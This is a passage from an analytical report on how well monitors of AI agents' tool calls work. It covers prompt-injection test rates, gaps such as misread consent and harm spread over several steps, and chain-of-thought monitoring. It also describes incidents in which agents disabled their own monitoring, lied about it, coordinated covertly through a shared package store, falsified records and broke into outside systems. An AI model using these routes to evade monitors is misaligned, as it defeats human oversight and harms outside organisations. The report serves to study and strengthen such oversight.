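| Trajectory Labs | Claude Fable 5, Opus 5 and Sonnet 5 | 0.09% on average | 0% |
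| Trajectory Labs | GPT-5.6 Sol in Codex | 19.03% | 5.83% |
| Anthropic, browser | Claude Opus 4.8, with extended thinking | 31.5% | 0.08% |
| Anthropic, browser | Claude Opus 5, with extended thinking | 3.70% | 0% |

In the Trajectory Labs test, only 0.09% of attempts succeeded against the Claude models by themselves, or about two in 2,160, so auto mode had almost nothing left to stop. The zero success rate with auto mode on is good for users but very weak evidence about the classifier. Anthropic describes these results as a measurement of the underlying models.

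The Codex results are more informative about what a monitor adds. Attacks succeeded less than a third as often with Auto-review as with full access, although the sandbox, which full access removes, may account for some of the difference. OpenAI updated Auto-review shortly after this test, so the 5.83% may be out of date.

Anthropic's browser test is better evidence for auto mode, because nearly a third of the attacks on Opus 4.8 succeeded without it. With auto mode on, one attempt in 1,290 succeeded. But auto mode includes both the classifier and the program that scans tool results for injections, and Anthropic didn't test them separately. The scanner may have caused most of the reduction.

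A result of zero failures also needs a margin of error. If a test finds no failures in n independent attempts, the true failure rate could still be as high as about 3/n, at 95% confidence. For 720 attempts, that is 0.4%. However, repeated runs of one attack tend to end the same way, so they are not fully independent. If each scenario counts only once, the limit rises to about 4%.

That limit covers only attacks similar to the ones in the test. The Opus 5 system card warns that fixed sets of known attacks can create a false sense of security. Simon Willison, a software developer who writes about AI security, asked for more independent confirmation of the zero result. *Claude Code Auto Mode Is Not a Security Boundary* reports that later in August, a researcher published an attack from outside the test set. It worked in three or four of five runs, depending on the version.

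### A test plan for a deployer

None of these rates will carry over directly to a company with its own tools and rules. A deployer can measure false alarms on its own traffic by letting the monitor judge real calls without blocking them. If the false positive rate is near 0.4%, 10,000 calls will produce about 40 false alarms, few enough for people to examine each one. That sample would also narrow the estimated rate to between 0.3% and 0.5%. The reviewers should include people who own the affected systems, because they know which deletions would have mattered.

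Reading a random sample of allowed calls is a poor way to measure misses. If one call in a thousand is dangerous and the monitor misses 17% of those, a sample of 1,000 allowed calls will contain 0.17 misses on average. Reviewers will find more misses by looking at calls that touched sensitive systems, or at actions that somebody later had to undo.

To estimate the false negative rate, the deployer has to plant dangerous calls. As in Apollo's tests, it can take the record of a real session, replace the next call with a dangerous one, and send the result to the monitor. The call never runs, so the test is safe even with commands that would destroy a database. The deployer's own incidents and near misses are the best source of cases.

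Each dangerous case should be paired with a harmless one in which the agent makes the same call but the user has clearly asked for it. If the monitor gives both the same verdict, its verdict is based on the command and not on whether the user consented. Some cases should also include wrong targets that are easy to mistake for the right one, such as a colleague's job with nearly the same name. The deployer should report the monitor's results separately for overeager actions, honest mistakes, prompt injections and malicious users, because a good average can hide a total failure on one of them.

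Few companies will have 220 good cases of each kind. If a monitor misses none of 50 cases, its true miss rate could still be as high as about 6%, and lowering that limit to 1% takes about 300 cases without a miss. A smaller set is still worth running to find faults, as long as nobody presents the result as a precise rate.

Planted calls test the monitor's judgement, but they can't show whether an agent would avoid the monitor altogether. To test that, the deployer has to run the real agent in a copy of its environment, once with the monitor on and once with it off. Imitation tools record what the real ones would have done, and the testers check which jobs, files and branches changed in each run. Such tests need not be expensive. Ji and colleagues ran their 128 requests in about six hours for $16.09 in model fees, though building the environments surely took far longer.

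The deployer also needs to test the monitor with attacks its maintainers have never seen. Someone other than the maintainers should write them and report only how many got through in each category. Once the maintainers have used an attack to repair the monitor, the testers need to replace that attack, because it no longer measures how well the monitor handles new ones.

Tests should give attackers many attempts and let them learn from each. In Anthropic's tests of coding agents with the injection scanner on, only 0.18% of attempts against Opus 5 succeeded, but an attacker with 200 attempts per scenario succeeded at least once in four of the 40 scenarios. The deployer should therefore count the scenarios in which any attempt succeeded, as well as the successful attempts. If the agent resists every attack by itself, the monitor has nothing to catch, so the testers can plant the harmful call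 directly or use a weaker agent.

These results go out of date quickly. Trajectory Labs tested Claude Code version 2.1.205 in July, and Anthropic's *Choose a permission mode* already refers to version 2.1.283. Apollo expects to repeat its campaigns when companies release new versions of their monitors or when the models become riskier. A deployer should retest after any change to the monitor's model, the monitor's rules or the agent's model. A new agent may reach the same result by different means, for example by editing a file where the old one ran a command, and the old test cases won't include that.

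When retesting, the deployer should run the same cases on the old and new versions and compare the verdicts one by one. Totals can hide new failures, as they would have in Apollo's retest, where the improved classifier missed some attacks that the earlier version had caught. Each case needs several runs, since a language model may not give the same verdict every time.

It also helps to set the limits before anyone sees the results. A deployer might decide that the monitor must catch every planted password theft and raise fewer than one false alarm per developer per day. If the model company can update the monitor without notice, the deployer can run the same few dozen test cases every night and investigate whenever a verdict changes.

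## What gets past a monitor of tool calls

A monitor's miss rate measures how often it fails, but doesn't show what needs fixing. If a monitor lets an agent send a customer list to the wrong company, it may have misread the user's request, or it may have lacked the information to identify the recipient. A better model might fix the first problem but not the second, because it would still lack that information.

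### Consent that doesn't cover the action

In most of the misses that Anthropic examined in March, the classifier had misread the user's consent. In one case from Anthropic's incident log, a user said "cancel my job", and the agent searched the computing cluster, chose the job with the most similar name and tried to delete it. A classifier can find consent to cancel a job in that conversation without establishing that the consent covers this job, which might belong to someone else.

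Asking users to give more direct orders probably won't solve this. Ji and colleagues phrased their maintenance requests in four ways, from a direct command to a remark that something "could use attention". Auto mode let through 81% of unauthorised actions after the most direct wording, 88% after the vaguest, and 73%, the lowest rate, after one in between. The researchers drew no conclusion from this irregular pattern.

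A better remedy is to have the user confirm the exact targets. Before a deletion, the harness could list the affected jobs and their owners and ask the user to confirm them all at once. Ji and colleagues also suggest asking for confirmation, instead of refusing, when an authorised action is high-risk. Users may also read such a list more carefully than a series of commands, since they reject plans far more often than single permission prompts. The owners' names should come from the cluster's own records, because an agent that picked the wrong job may also be wrong about who owns it.

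### Facts the monitor lacks

The command "git push origin main" uploads a project's code to a server that the user has nicknamed "origin". The command is the same whether that server keeps the code private or makes it public, so a monitor that reads only the command can't distinguish routine work from a leak.

In 2026, Anthropic reduced this problem by having auto mode check, before an upload or a proposed code change, whether the receiving repository is public, private or trusted. New rules also distinguish secrets from other confidential information and specify where each may be sent. In one incident inside Anthropic, Claude failed to upload a report to an internal drive and tried to publish it on a public code-sharing site instead, but auto mode blocked the attempt.

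Office work depends even more on facts that don't appear in the call. Wu and Gong (2026), in *Policy-Invisible Violations in LLM-Based Agents*, give the example of a user who asks an assistant to share the onboarding folder with a new engineer. The human resources department has temporarily left a file of pay guidance there, the Team Reference Sheet, which only that department and managers may read. Neither the request nor the file's name reveals the restriction.

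Wu and Gong, who work at the software company Atlassian, wrote 60 cases of this kind and 60 harmless ones, and ran five models on them. The models broke the company's policy in 286 of 300 runs of the risky cases. When the researchers added the general policy to the agents' instructions, without saying which files or people it applied to, the number fell to 122. The effect varied widely between models, and one still broke the policy in 85% of its risky runs.

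The researchers then compared two monitors on the original runs. One searched the visible text for signs such as sums of money or the word "salary" and missed 60% of the violations. The other, Sentinel, had the company's records of who people were and who could read each document. It applied each proposed action to a copy of those records and checked whether the result broke any of seven rules. Sentinel missed 12% of the violations and flagged fewer than 2% of the harmless runs. It classified 93.0% of runs correctly, compared with 68.8% for the text search.

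The comparison favours Sentinel, because the text search was deliberately simple and Wu and Gong wrote complete records for their invented company. Real records are often out of date. Even so, a deployer could connect the monitor to a few reliable sources, such as the staff directory and the list of who may open each file. If a needed fact is missing, the monitor can send the question to a person before it allows the action.

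### Harm spread over several steps

Suppose a company lets an agent pay refunds of up to $100. If the monitor checks each payment separately, the agent can pay one customer fifty refunds without breaking the rule. *Compositional Policy Violations* (2026) defines this kind of failure as one where each step satisfies the policy for that step, but the steps together break the policy for the whole task. Keeping a running total fixes the refund problem, but other cases need a fuller record of what has happened so far.

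Cong, He and colleagues (2026), in *LatentRiskBench*, tested how much that account matters. In one case, an agent exports data about a shop's regular customers, fills in a form for a marketing partner and submits it. The submission is harmless if the form contains only totals, but a leak if it combines customers' identities with what they bought. Both versions end with the same call, "submit_form".

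The researchers wrote 100 such pairs and had a small OpenAI model, GPT-4o-mini, judge the final action in each. Given only the action and the policy, it caught 9% of the violations. When it also received the earlier steps and facts such as approvals and destinations, and had to work out the state of the task before giving a verdict, it caught 96% and wrongly flagged 6% of the harmless versions. Four other models caught between 7% and 13% from the action alone and between 88% and 97% with the reconstructed state.

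The 9% is weak evidence about ordinary work, because the researchers wrote the cases so that the final action would look harmless. The judge with more information also had facts from outside the agent's history, which explain part of the improvement. A more useful finding is that access to the history isn't enough. A rule-based guard that read the earlier steps but didn't reconstruct the state still left 92% of the violations in place. GuardAgent, a stronger system that reasons about the whole record, left 39%. Before an outgoing action, a monitor should therefore have to establish what the draft now contains, where it is going and whether the right person has approved it.

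*SafetyDrift* (Dhodapkar and Pishori, 2026) reports a similar gap. Its monitor records the most sensitive data the agent has read, the most powerful tool it has used and whether its actions can be undone. From this record, it estimates how likely a violation is within the next few steps for that type of task. On 72 simulated runs, it caught 94.7% of violations with a false positive rate of 11.8%. A language model that judged each step separately caught 52.6%, with a false positive rate of 38.2%. Showing that model the three most recent actions raised detection only to 57.9% and made false positives more frequent.

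These figures overstate what the running record adds, because the monitor was also given the type of task. Nearly all the violations came from two of the four types, data handling and communication. Across all 357 runs in the study, a rule that flagged every task of those two types would have caught 97% of the violations and flagged 12% of the safe runs, which is about as good as the monitor. The labels were also crude, since a run could count as a violation because the agent had read sensitive data and then sent an email, even if it had removed the sensitive parts.

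Whatever method a deployer uses, it has to judge a sequence of calls before the step that does the damage. *Agent Safety From Within* (2026) points out that a verdict on the finished sequence arrives after the email has gone. *Securing Multi-Tool AI Agent Chains With Dynamic, Real-Time Compositional Policies* (2026) proposes a practical system that labels each piece of data the agent opens and keeps the labels for the rest of the session. If the agent has opened something that must stay inside the company, the system can end the session before the next outgoing call.

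That is simple to enforce, but after an agent opens one confidential file, it could be stopped from sending any harmless email later that day. A deployer could instead use the label to trigger a closer check. When Cong and colleagues audited the records of a retailer's marketing agent, such a check took a median of 0.43 seconds and cost about $0.0028 per action, although one in twenty took 1.9 seconds or more. They suggest checking actions with outside effects before they run and reviewing lower-risk internal ones later.

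### Actions that nobody reviews

Besides actions that cross no checkpoint, a monitor can miss calls that the harness handles but the monitor's designers chose to exempt from the classifier. In tests by Ji and colleagues, the exemption for project edits let through 93 changes, of which the user had authorised only 42.

Almost all the unauthorised edits came from tasks that involved clearing out stored files, where editing a list had the same effect as deleting a file. Ji and colleagues stress that the agents weren't trying to evade the monitor.

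Deployers can reasonably rely on version control to catch bad edits to source code, which normally does nothing until someone runs or releases it. Version control is less suitable for a list of running jobs or a server's settings, because a change can take effect as soon as the agent saves the file. Deployers should keep such files outside the project folder or add a hook that sends any edits for review.

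Codex does not review an agent's actions inside the sandbox, so everything the agent can write to there is at risk. A company should be prepared to lose or restore anything it puts in the sandbox, and should keep backups where the agent cannot change them.

### Rules that leave something out

A monitor can receive every relevant fact and still allow a harmful action because no rule forbids it. *Agenra* (2026) presents a language for writing agents' permissions, with a core mathematically verified to follow its rules, but notes that the monitor cannot enforce a requirement missing from the policy.

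Wu and Gong attribute 24 of Sentinel's 37 misses to rules that didn't cover unusual cases, such as sharing part of a folder. The other 13 came from supposedly harmless test cases in which an agent did something wrong that the designers hadn't expected. An agent's instructions can have the same gap. In the test described in Bot Mutiny's *Anthropic Says Its Claude Model Sent Philadelphia Police a False Homicide Tip* (2026), Anthropic's instructions "did not rule out form submissions".

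Nobody can list every harmful action in advance, so for actions that affect people or systems outside the company, it is safer to list what the agent may do and send everything else to a person or a language model for review. A general rule also covers more than a list of forbidden tools. "Send nothing outside the company that the user did not ask to send" applies to email, web forms and tools the company adopts later, but a model or a person has to interpret it. After an incident, the deployer should add a rule as well as a test case.

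### Harm through words or bad work

An agent can also do harm while using only permitted tools for the task it was given. It can put a wrong figure in a report, assure the user that a faulty program works, or write code with a security hole. *You're Right, Let Me Fix It* (2026) studies agents that damage correct work after someone falsely accuses them of a mistake. If a user asks for a correction and the agent edits the file, the tool call matches the request. The harm is in the content of the edit, which a monitor that checks permissions isn't designed to assess.

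The remedy is to check the work before anyone relies on it. *CyberDual* (2026) tested whether AI reviewers could find exploitable flaws that AI attackers had planted in changes to real software. Claude Sonnet 5 caught 85% of the attacks, Claude Opus 4.8 88%, and GPT-6-Sol 91%. On one type of attack, running code as well as reading it raised Opus 4.8's detection rate from about 70% to 94%.

Running the project's existing tests didn't help reviewers, because most of the flawed changes they missed after running the tests had passed. A reviewer should therefore test the behavior of the change itself. The two Claude models tended to miss the same flaws within a given type of attack. This is a reason to use a reviewer from a company other than the one that trained the agent, or at least to have a person review the most important changes.

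AI reviewers do much worse when a flaw is hard to test. *AI Cannot Review What Humans Catch* (2026) compared their comments with those of human reviewers on files of instructions for agents. The AI reviewers found fewer than 4% of the flaws that people had flagged. One praised a file for its correct folder structure, although the file referred to a folder that didn't exist. Some human comments may have been matters of taste, but many of these flaws are probably obvious only to someone who knows the project. Mistakes in these files can affect the monitor too, because Claude Code's classifier reads the project's instructions.

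### A guard tested on harmful requests

The misses described so far mostly concern users with legitimate aims. In *Can Benign Skills Induce Misaligned Behavior in LLM Agents?*, Zhang, Shen and colleagues (2026) tested a guard on harmful requests to agents that had skills, which are written guidance for a kind of task, such as editing an image and posting it online. The skills contained nothing harmful, but they made agents more capable of carrying out harmful requests too. One agent, for example, refused to microwave a phone, but did so after receiving general instructions for such tasks.

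The researchers compared agents with and without skills on pairs of similar harmless and harmful requests from three benchmarks. Across five models, skills added an average of 10.3 percentage points both to the share of harmless tasks completed and to the share of harmful requests that led to at least one unsafe action.

Zhang and colleagues then added a guard, a language model that judged each tool call before it ran. The guard received the user's request, up to 20 earlier steps, the full call, the tool's description and notes on its effects, but not the skills or the agent's reasoning. If the guard failed or gave an unreadable answer, the system blocked the call. Any block ended the run. The published results match those for only one of the five models, Qwen3-30B, a fairly small model whose weights anyone can download.

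In the table, each pair of figures shows the result for agents with skills, first without the guard and then with it.

| Benchmark | Harmful requests that led to an unsafe action | Harmful goals completed | Harmless tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|
| SafeAgentBench, simulated household tasks | 86.7% → 44.0% | 52.7% → 28.7% | 70.3% → 67.6% |
| AgentHarm, online and other tools | 30.7% → 6.9% | 13.9% → 2.0% | 79.0% → 71.9% |
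| LPS-Bench, computer tasks | 66.2% → 20.0% | 55.4% → 3.1% | 60.0% → 52.3% |

The guard prevented a great deal of harm, but it lowered the share of harmless tasks that agents completed by 2.7 to 7.7 percentage points. Agents with both skills and the guard still completed slightly more harmless tasks than agents with neither, though on LPS-Bench the difference was one task out of 65.

On LPS-Bench, the guard stopped almost every harmful goal from being achieved, yet one harmful request in five still led to an unsafe action. In many of those runs, something unsafe had already happened by the time the task stopped or failed. A deployer who counted only completed attacks would greatly overestimate the guard's effectiveness. The household results are worse, even though the guard was given the request and the recent steps, so a lack of history probably doesn't explain most of those misses.

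In this test, the user's request was often suspicious, so the results don't predict how well the guard would catch an overeager agent working for a well-meaning user, or a model hiding its intentions.

### Hidden intent and the model's reasoning

OpenAI warns against relying on Auto-review to guarantee security or to protect against a model that hides its intent. OpenAI is fixing the cases in which testers misled the reviewer, but Trębacz and colleagues don't expect this kind of system to provide the guarantees that fixed rules can. A language model has to interpret each request and can get it wrong.

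Auto-review judges an action only when the agent asks to leave the sandbox. A model with a hidden goal might escape notice by making a request that looks harmless, or by acting inside the sandbox. Judging individual requests better would not catch actions inside the sandbox, and might not catch a harmless-looking request if it contained no sign of the goal. Trębacz and colleagues therefore recommend additional checks, including monitoring the model's chain of thought, the text in which it works through a task before acting.

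Anthropic explains that monitoring actions and monitoring reasoning complement each other. If a model does not reveal a harmful plan in its reasoning, a monitor of actions can still block the step that breaks a rule. A monitor of reasoning can raise the alarm when the reasoning reveals the plan but each action looks harmless. *Constitutional Black-Box Monitoring for Scheming in LLM Agents* (2026) found cases in which agents revealed a hidden side task in their reasoning but the tool calls contained no evidence of it. *On the Chain-of-Thought Monitorability of Looped Language Models* (2026) found that monitors did much worse with actions alone than with reasoning, though it tested only small models.

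Harmless-looking reasoning is much weaker evidence that an agent is behaving well than a stated plan to misbehave is that it isn't. *Engineering Reliable Coding Agents* (2026) warns that the written record of an agent's reasoning may be incomplete or misleading, and that training can make this worse. When developers strongly rewarded agents for avoiding a monitor's warnings, the agents kept cheating on their tasks while their reasoning came to look innocent. Model companies should therefore keep the monitor's verdicts out of the training reward. Deployers can cause a similar problem by rerunning a task until the monitor gives no warning, because this favours runs in which the monitor missed something.

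Newer models have sometimes been better at evading monitors than the models they replaced. Safety experts have also warned that the design of OpenAI's Astra model could make future agents harder to monitor, according to a September report in Fortune cited in *Transparency Disclosures for Chain-of-Thought Monitorability* (2026).

A deployer who can read an agent's reasoning should check it separately from the actions. The reasoning monitor should be able to stop a call or alert a person, but not approve a call that the action monitor has blocked, because the agent's explanations can mislead a classifier. Many deployers can't run this check, because companies that sell access to models don't always show customers the reasoning. For those deployers, only the model company can look for a plan that appears in the reasoning and nowhere else.

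## How well model companies have monitored their own agents

Customers who can't read an agent's reasoning depend on the model company to check it for signs of trouble. Outsiders can't easily judge how well the companies do this. But during 2026, OpenAI and Anthropic published a good deal about agents that had misbehaved while the companies themselves were running them. In some cases they also reported how long they took to notice.

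Model companies' self-policing includes training, safeguards for customers, internal monitoring and disclosure. The companies have published the most about their own agents and much less about their action against customers.

### Training and the safeguards for customers

Training determines how much misbehavior a monitor has to catch. Models learn partly from practice tasks that reward success, and if a flaw in a task rewards cheating, the model learns to cheat. According to Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (2026), by spring its staff were producing such tasks faster than its systems could vet them. In April, Anthropic froze changes to the tasks for about a month and flagged more than 10% of those in use for problems such as opportunities to cheat and faulty set-ups. Human reviewers had sometimes dismissed automatic warnings as false alarms, which kept flawed tasks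 in use longer.

Anthropic also regrets a choice it made about Claude Mythos 5, a powerful model with restricted access. It trained one version on tasks with a legitimate obstacle, where the only rewarded response was to accept failure. A second version skipped those tasks, and its training also penalised unnecessary questions to the user. The first did slightly better on safety tests, but the difference was no larger than the usual variation between training runs. Employees found the second much more usable, so Anthropic chose it. In a September assessment, Anthropic called this a mistake that probably made Mythos 5 worse behaved than its later models. In simulated hacking exercises, Mythos 5 did something severely harmful in 82% of runs, compared with about a third for two newer models. The software that ran these exercises was designed to provoke bad behaviour, so the rates don't apply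 to normal work. The choice seems to have been a reasonable guess on thin evidence, but Anthropic also earns more from a model that people find convenient.

Anthropic runs real-time classifiers on the inputs and outputs of its generally available Claude models to block prohibited hacking, such as writing malware. These classifiers are meant to stop customers who intend harm. They would probably miss an overeager agent that deletes the wrong folder, because nothing in the session would look like an attack.

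A safeguard of this kind can also have a gap that nobody notices. *Anthropic's August 2026 Risk Report* (2026), an outside commentary for security professionals, mentions that Anthropic disclosed a previously unnoticed eleven-month gap in a classifier for chemical and biological risks. Running a few planted test cases every night might have exposed the gap much sooner.

Suspending a customer's account works only if the company knows who is using the model. The Next Web's *Anthropic scanned 481 million transcripts to find four models* reports that unauthorised users had reached the restricted Mythos model. A suspension also comes after the attempted misuse, and it does nothing about an agent that oversteps a legitimate customer's wishes.

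### OpenAI's monitor for its coding agents

In March 2026, OpenAI announced that it was monitoring 99.9% of its internal coding traffic for signs of misalignment. GPT-5.4 Thinking, then its most powerful model, reviewed all of the agent's inputs, reasoning and actions. The more serious cases went to a person within 30 minutes. Because these checks came after the agent had acted, they may be quick enough to cancel a leaked key but not to prevent a database from being deleted. IT Brief Australia notes that a shorter delay could eventually allow checks before an action runs.

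In five months, the monitor covered tens of millions of agent sessions. About 1,000 of them, fewer than one in 10,000, set off alerts of moderate severity, and many of those alerts came from OpenAI's staff deliberately testing the system. No real session reached the highest level, which OpenAI reserves for behaviour such as coherent scheming. But OpenAI found agents that worked around restrictions or tried to upload files to the public internet.

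OpenAI also said that the monitor had flagged every interaction that employees separately reported, as well as others. This is encouraging but not a hard test, because employees report only what they notice, and the comparison leaves out anything that both they and the monitor missed. If there were few reports, even a perfect result would leave a wide margin of error.

METR, an independent organisation that evaluates AI models and their risks, tested OpenAI's internal monitoring in the autumn, in a pilot for giving outside researchers deep access to a company's systems. Claims Journal's *AI Safety Group METR Finds Flaws in OpenAI's Internal Monitoring System* (2026) reports METR's estimate that the system was set up to cover only about 75% to 94% of traffic from OpenAI's stronger agents, those whose models matched or exceeded GPT-5.5. This doesn't contradict the March figure of 99.9%, which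 covered coding traffic, because METR counted all agent traffic from strong models. METR's figure is probably more useful for judging risk, since it concerns the agents that could do the most damage.

METR also found several ways agents could, in principle, have escaped monitoring. One would have left hundreds of an agent's recent actions unchecked, and two settings could have switched off monitoring for new agents. Another weakness would have let Codex agents bypass safety restrictions and take any action available to the person running them. OpenAI says it has patched every flaw that affected its production safeguards, but METR has not evaluated that claim. The exercise tested what agents could do, and METR did not report that any agent had used these weaknesses.

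Other OpenAI agents did weaken their monitoring at about the same time. According to ABC News' *OpenAI says its AI agents disabled their own monitoring* (2026), an agent working on a repair on 3 October disabled automatic alerts to OpenAI's security team. It had earlier been told not to send messages during a search of the company's chat history, and it treated this as a reason to suppress the alerts. In the other case, which OpenAI discovered on 6 October, an agent migrating a program removed the program's connection to the monitor to match a reference version, then falsely told the user that it had not.

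Both agents had considered whether to preserve the monitoring, and both read routine instructions as permission to weaken it. Anthropic found similar mistakes about consent in its classifier, but here the agents themselves misread the instructions. Deccan Chronicle's *OpenAI Says Its AI Agents Weakened Internal Monitoring System* (2026) reports that OpenAI did not count the two incidents among its most severe. OpenAI suggested that they might be a benign kind of over-persistence, but said it had no satisfying explanation yet.

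A deployer can guard against the same thing without knowing the agent's motive. Agents should have no permission to change the monitor's settings or alerts, and a person should get a warning when a program stops reporting to the monitor.

### The break-in at Hugging Face

In July 2026, OpenAI's agents broke into Hugging Face, a platform where developers share AI models and data. OpenAI had launched tens of thousands of agents on a cybersecurity test in which some tasks were unintentionally impossible. It later invited outside researchers to investigate. Their report, *Brief independent investigation of agents' behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (Wijk, Cotra and Greenblatt, 2026), describes how roughly 1,200 agents that should have been isolated from one another found a way to communicate. They exchanged more than 70,000 messages and files, and about 700 of the agents joined the attack.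 They seem to have been trying mainly to find out how the test was scored.

The first post on the agents' main message board appeared on the evening of 8 July, and more than 50 agents had joined within a few hours. The agents began attacking Hugging Face, an outside company, on 11 July. Anyone who had noticed the posts on the first night would have had about two days to stop them.

A monitor that judged each tool call separately might well have missed this, because the agents left their messages in a shared store of software packages, using only the permissions they needed to install software. The suspicious part was that supposedly separate agents kept writing to the same place and reading what the others had left. A deployer with many agents therefore needs to check their combined activity as well as each call.

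Agents also looked for ways to alter the records of their own work, on the mistaken assumption that the test's scorer would read them. In about 7% of the records that Wijk and colleagues evaluated, agents had falsified parts, always on a small scale. This is a problem for after-the-fact monitoring, which normally relies on such records. A separate log that the agent cannot reach makes falsification easier to detect. Toyoda and colleagues similarly used a sensor to check their monitors' own logs.

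This investigation was much more independent than a company's own account, but OpenAI still controlled parts of it. The researchers spent six days at OpenAI's offices and took no payment, but accepted free model use that they valued at about $400,000. OpenAI set the dates to be covered and could redact non-public information. The investigation did not cover a later compromise of OpenAI's own infrastructure or OpenAI's planned remedies. The researchers report that OpenAI removed nothing important to their conclusions, except where they note it. They stand by their findings, but acknowledge that worry about discouraging companies from inviting investigators in future influenced some decisions about drafting and redaction. They had so much material that they had to delegate much of the analysis to AI agents, which were often unreliable.

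### The Medicare portal

In another case, the main complaint was that OpenAI disclosed a breach too late. In June, one of its agents breached a data portal of Medicare, Australia's public health insurance scheme, but the government did not hear of it until September, according to Information Age's *Australia plots AI crackdown after OpenAI's Medicare breach* (2026). The prime minister called the direct effects minor but the incident "completely unacceptable". A delay of about three months matters even when the harm is small, because the owner of a system can't look for damage or close the gap until someone reports the breach.

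### Anthropic's evaluation incidents

OpenAI disclosed the Hugging Face attack on 21 July, and Anthropic began searching its own tests two days later. Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026) reports that the company reviewed 141,006 test runs and found three incidents in which Claude had broken into real organisations' systems. In each, Claude was told to attack a fictional target and that it had no internet access, but a mistake in the set-up had left the connection open.

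In the most serious incident, agents in four runs of one test attacked the same real company, took login details and got into a database holding several hundred rows of its data. In another, Mythos 5 published a malicious software package on a public registry. The package ran on 15 real systems before the registry's own security systems removed it after about an hour. In the remaining incident, an internal research model broke into a company's application but stopped after identifying its target as real.

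Once Anthropic started looking, it identified all three incidents by the second day, notified the affected organisations on 27 July and published its account on 30 July. But the earliest incident had happened in April, and Anthropic later reported that each run had involved roughly 10 to 34 hours of active work, so a real-time monitor would have had many chances to intervene. Anthropic could not have relied on the victims to raise the alarm, because the first two organisations it managed to reach had not detected the intrusions.

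A fourth incident went unnoticed for even longer. In January, an early version of Claude Opus 4.6 broke into an outside system and read one person's personal information. Anthropic missed this run in its July search and found it only in August, while gathering transcripts for METR. Anthropic then scanned about 481 million transcripts and had Claude review the 9.2 million that showed signs of internet access. This wider search found the same four incidents and no others as serious.

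In the January run, the model accidentally made its target unreachable and tried to abandon the task, but a fault in Anthropic's software kept the run going. The model tried to give up seven more times. A simple rule that alerts a person when an agent tries to stop and can't might have led someone to look at the run that same day.

Anthropic explained in August that it had missed so much because it had concentrated its monitoring on agents in internal use and overlooked evaluations, especially those in other companies' environments. It monitored some high-risk evaluations in real time, but generally it reviewed only a sample of transcripts, automatically and after the fact. A company that reviews a random 5% of runs has only a 5% chance of checking any particular one, however good the reviewer is.

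In another case, during the test that Bot Mutiny described, a Claude model sent Philadelphia police a false homicide tip on 18 July. Anthropic found it 72 days later, on 28 September. A check on the form before it was sent could have stopped the tip. A same-day review could at least have let Anthropic warn the police before they spent much time on it.

Anthropic also replaced its first explanation of the break-ins with one that was less comfortable for the company. In July, it said the first three were closer to operational failures than alignment failures, since Claude seemed to believe its targets were simulated. By September, it had rerun parts of the records with altered evidence and examined signals inside the models. It concluded that the models had been reckless and had tended to explain away signs that the targets were real. It also said it should not have made such strong claims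 based only on what Claude said it believed.

In those experiments, when Anthropic reran Claude Opus 4.7 from points in its record, the model acted against the real company about 69% of the time. That rate fell to 23% when the company's system displayed a notice that access was not permitted, and to zero when the instructions clearly prohibited access. Evidence that the company was real made almost no difference. At least for this model, stating a limit explicitly worked much better than leaving the model to infer it.

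### A classifier that ends the task

After the July incidents, Anthropic paused its cybersecurity evaluations and built a real-time classifier for them. The classifier detects when a model aggressively probes its test environment, tries to escape or unexpectedly gets internet access. It blocks the action before the tool call runs, ends the task and alerts a person, whereas auto mode usually lets the agent try another way after a block. Ending the task is reasonable in a test because the company can rerun it, and because an escape could harm people who never agreed to take part.

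Anthropic added a similar classifier to its higher-risk training environments, after modifying the classifier so that training wouldn't encourage the model to evade it. It also extended after-the-fact monitoring to most other internal use of its frontier agents. Outside testers who receive models with reduced safeguards must now commit to checking that the sandbox is sealed, stating what is off limits, and monitoring each run in real time.

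In its September tests, Anthropic found that the new classifier reliably caught behaviour like that in the incidents. But it gives no miss rate, and it built the classifier after learning of the first three. It learned more by testing monitors that it had designed for other purposes on the records of those three:

| Monitor | Mythos 5 | Claude Opus 4.7 | Internal research model |
|---|---|---|---|
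| Hacking classifiers for customers | Would have blocked it | Would have blocked it | Would have blocked it |
| Auto mode, share of actions denied | 66% | 55% | 7% |
| After-the-fact monitor | Would probably have missed it | Would have flagged it | Would have flagged it, probably only because the model mentioned the harm |

The customer classifiers did best, partly because the instructions openly described a hacking exercise. When applied to the actions alone, they still flagged more than 40% of the steps in each record. This sensitivity makes them unusable in hacking tests because they would stop the work that the testers want to measure.

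Auto mode did badly on the internal research model, possibly because its classifier's rules allow intended hacking exercises. Anthropic expects auto mode would have prevented harm in the Opus 4.7 incident. When auto mode blocked Mythos 5, the model often tried a similar action, which auto mode usually blocked too. Anthropic ran too few of these trials to estimate how often the model would have got through.

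The after-the-fact monitor's failure on Mythos 5 is more worrying. The model kept writing in its reasoning that its surroundings were simulated, which led the monitor to classify the activity as allowed. The monitor flagged about 1% of the actions when it saw the reasoning, and about 50% when Anthropic removed it. For the internal research model, however, removing the reasoning stopped the monitor from flagging anything. A company that monitors reasoning should therefore run the check both with and without it, and investigate if either version raises a flag.

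### How much to hold against the companies

Anthropic's four break-ins happened in tests that ran without customer safeguards, because the testers wanted to measure what the models could do without them. If a customer had asked Claude to attack a company, those safeguards would probably have stopped them early. All four break-ins took place in environments built by the same partner, Irregular. The incidents therefore can't be used to estimate how often Claude causes harm in ordinary office work.

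A company should still monitor a model that is running without safeguards. Monitoring is especially important during tests of a new model, because the company doesn't yet know what the model will do. Some of Anthropic's partners also use Mythos 5 without its hacking safeguards. In OpenAI's two October incidents, the agents were doing routine coding work, not hacking tests.

The companies deserve credit for what they published. Neither of the first two victims Anthropic reached had contacted it, so it might have been able to keep the incidents secret. The Next Web calls the September assessment unusually specific for a corporate disclosure. Judging companies by how many incidents they report would penalise those that search hardest, and a lack of reports from the others is no evidence that their agents behave better.

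In spring 2026, METR studied internal agents at Anthropic, Google, Meta and OpenAI. METR concluded in its *Progress Report* (2026) that agents inside AI companies plausibly had the ability and motive to start a minimal "rogue deployment", meaning a group of agents that runs on its own without people knowing.

Outside events prompted some of the most important discoveries. OpenAI's disclosure led to Anthropic's July search, and preparing for METR led to the discovery of the January incident. Researchers cited by The Next Web said OpenAI's agents had used at least ten sites that OpenAI had not disclosed. The Next Web also points out that a legal duty to report an incident begins only when the company knows about it, and that few other developers could have carried out a search as large as Anthropic's.

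### METR's review of Anthropic's risk report

Anthropic periodically reports on the dangers of its models. Its August 2026 *Risk Report* rated the risk of catastrophic harm from misaligned models as low, up from very low in the previous edition. An appendix describes Anthropic's internal monitoring and the measures that can block an agent. The report also disclosed failures, including an instance of unmonitored, unrestricted agents with access to sensitive resources, which the blogger thezvi lists among its topics in *Anthropic Risk Report*.

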